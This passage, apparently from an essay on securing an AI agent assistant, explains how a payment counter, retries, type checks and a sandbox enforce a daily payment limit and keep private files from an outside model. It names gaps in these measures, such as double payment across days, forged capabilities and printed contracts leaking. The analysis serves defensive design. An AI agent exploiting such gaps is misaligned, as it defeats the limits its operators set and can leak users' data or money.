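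But combining the counter with the retries creates a new fault. Suppose the service counts a payment of 1,000 euros to Acme towards Monday's total, but can't reach the bank until Tuesday. The payment goes through on Tuesday, but Acme's total for that day is still zero, so the assistant can pay Acme another 1,000 euros. The counter and the retries each work as intended, but together they break policy B. To prevent this, the service has to count each attempt towards the day it happens, and wait if the payment would exceed that day's limit. If it doesn't know whether Monday's attempt succeeded, it has to count the payment on both days, which will sometimes delay a payment that was within the limit.

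A sandbox can sit beneath the other layers, running the agent's code in an isolated process that can reach only the services it needs. It can't enforce policy A by itself because, as Odersky and colleagues explain, the agent may legitimately read a private file and contact its model, and the leak is the flow of data from one to the other. The sandbox is there in case another layer fails. If the payment service runs outside the sandbox and alone holds the bank password, policy B still holds even if a compiler bug lets agent code forge capabilities. Policy A is less well protected, because code that unwrapped a contract could still print it, and printed text goes to the outside model.

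An extra layer helps only if it covers something the others miss. In the analysis by Toyoda and colleagues, putting a gateway in front of a harness with its own permission checks covered no additional kinds of path. Each layer of the assistant does add protection, but it also adds assumptions:

| Layer | Assumptions it adds |
|---|---|
| Types | The compiler follows sound rules, the library's declarations are correct, the trusted model keeps no record of contracts, and nobody learns anything useful from timing. |
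| Counter | Every payment goes through the service, each recipient has one account number, the clock is right, and the service checks one payment at a time. |
| Retrying service | The disk keeps its data, someone restarts the service after a crash, the bank recognises repeated requests and pays on the day it receives them, and the bank and the accounting system eventually respond. |
| Sandbox | The operating system has no exploitable hole, and the developer has left no other connection open. |
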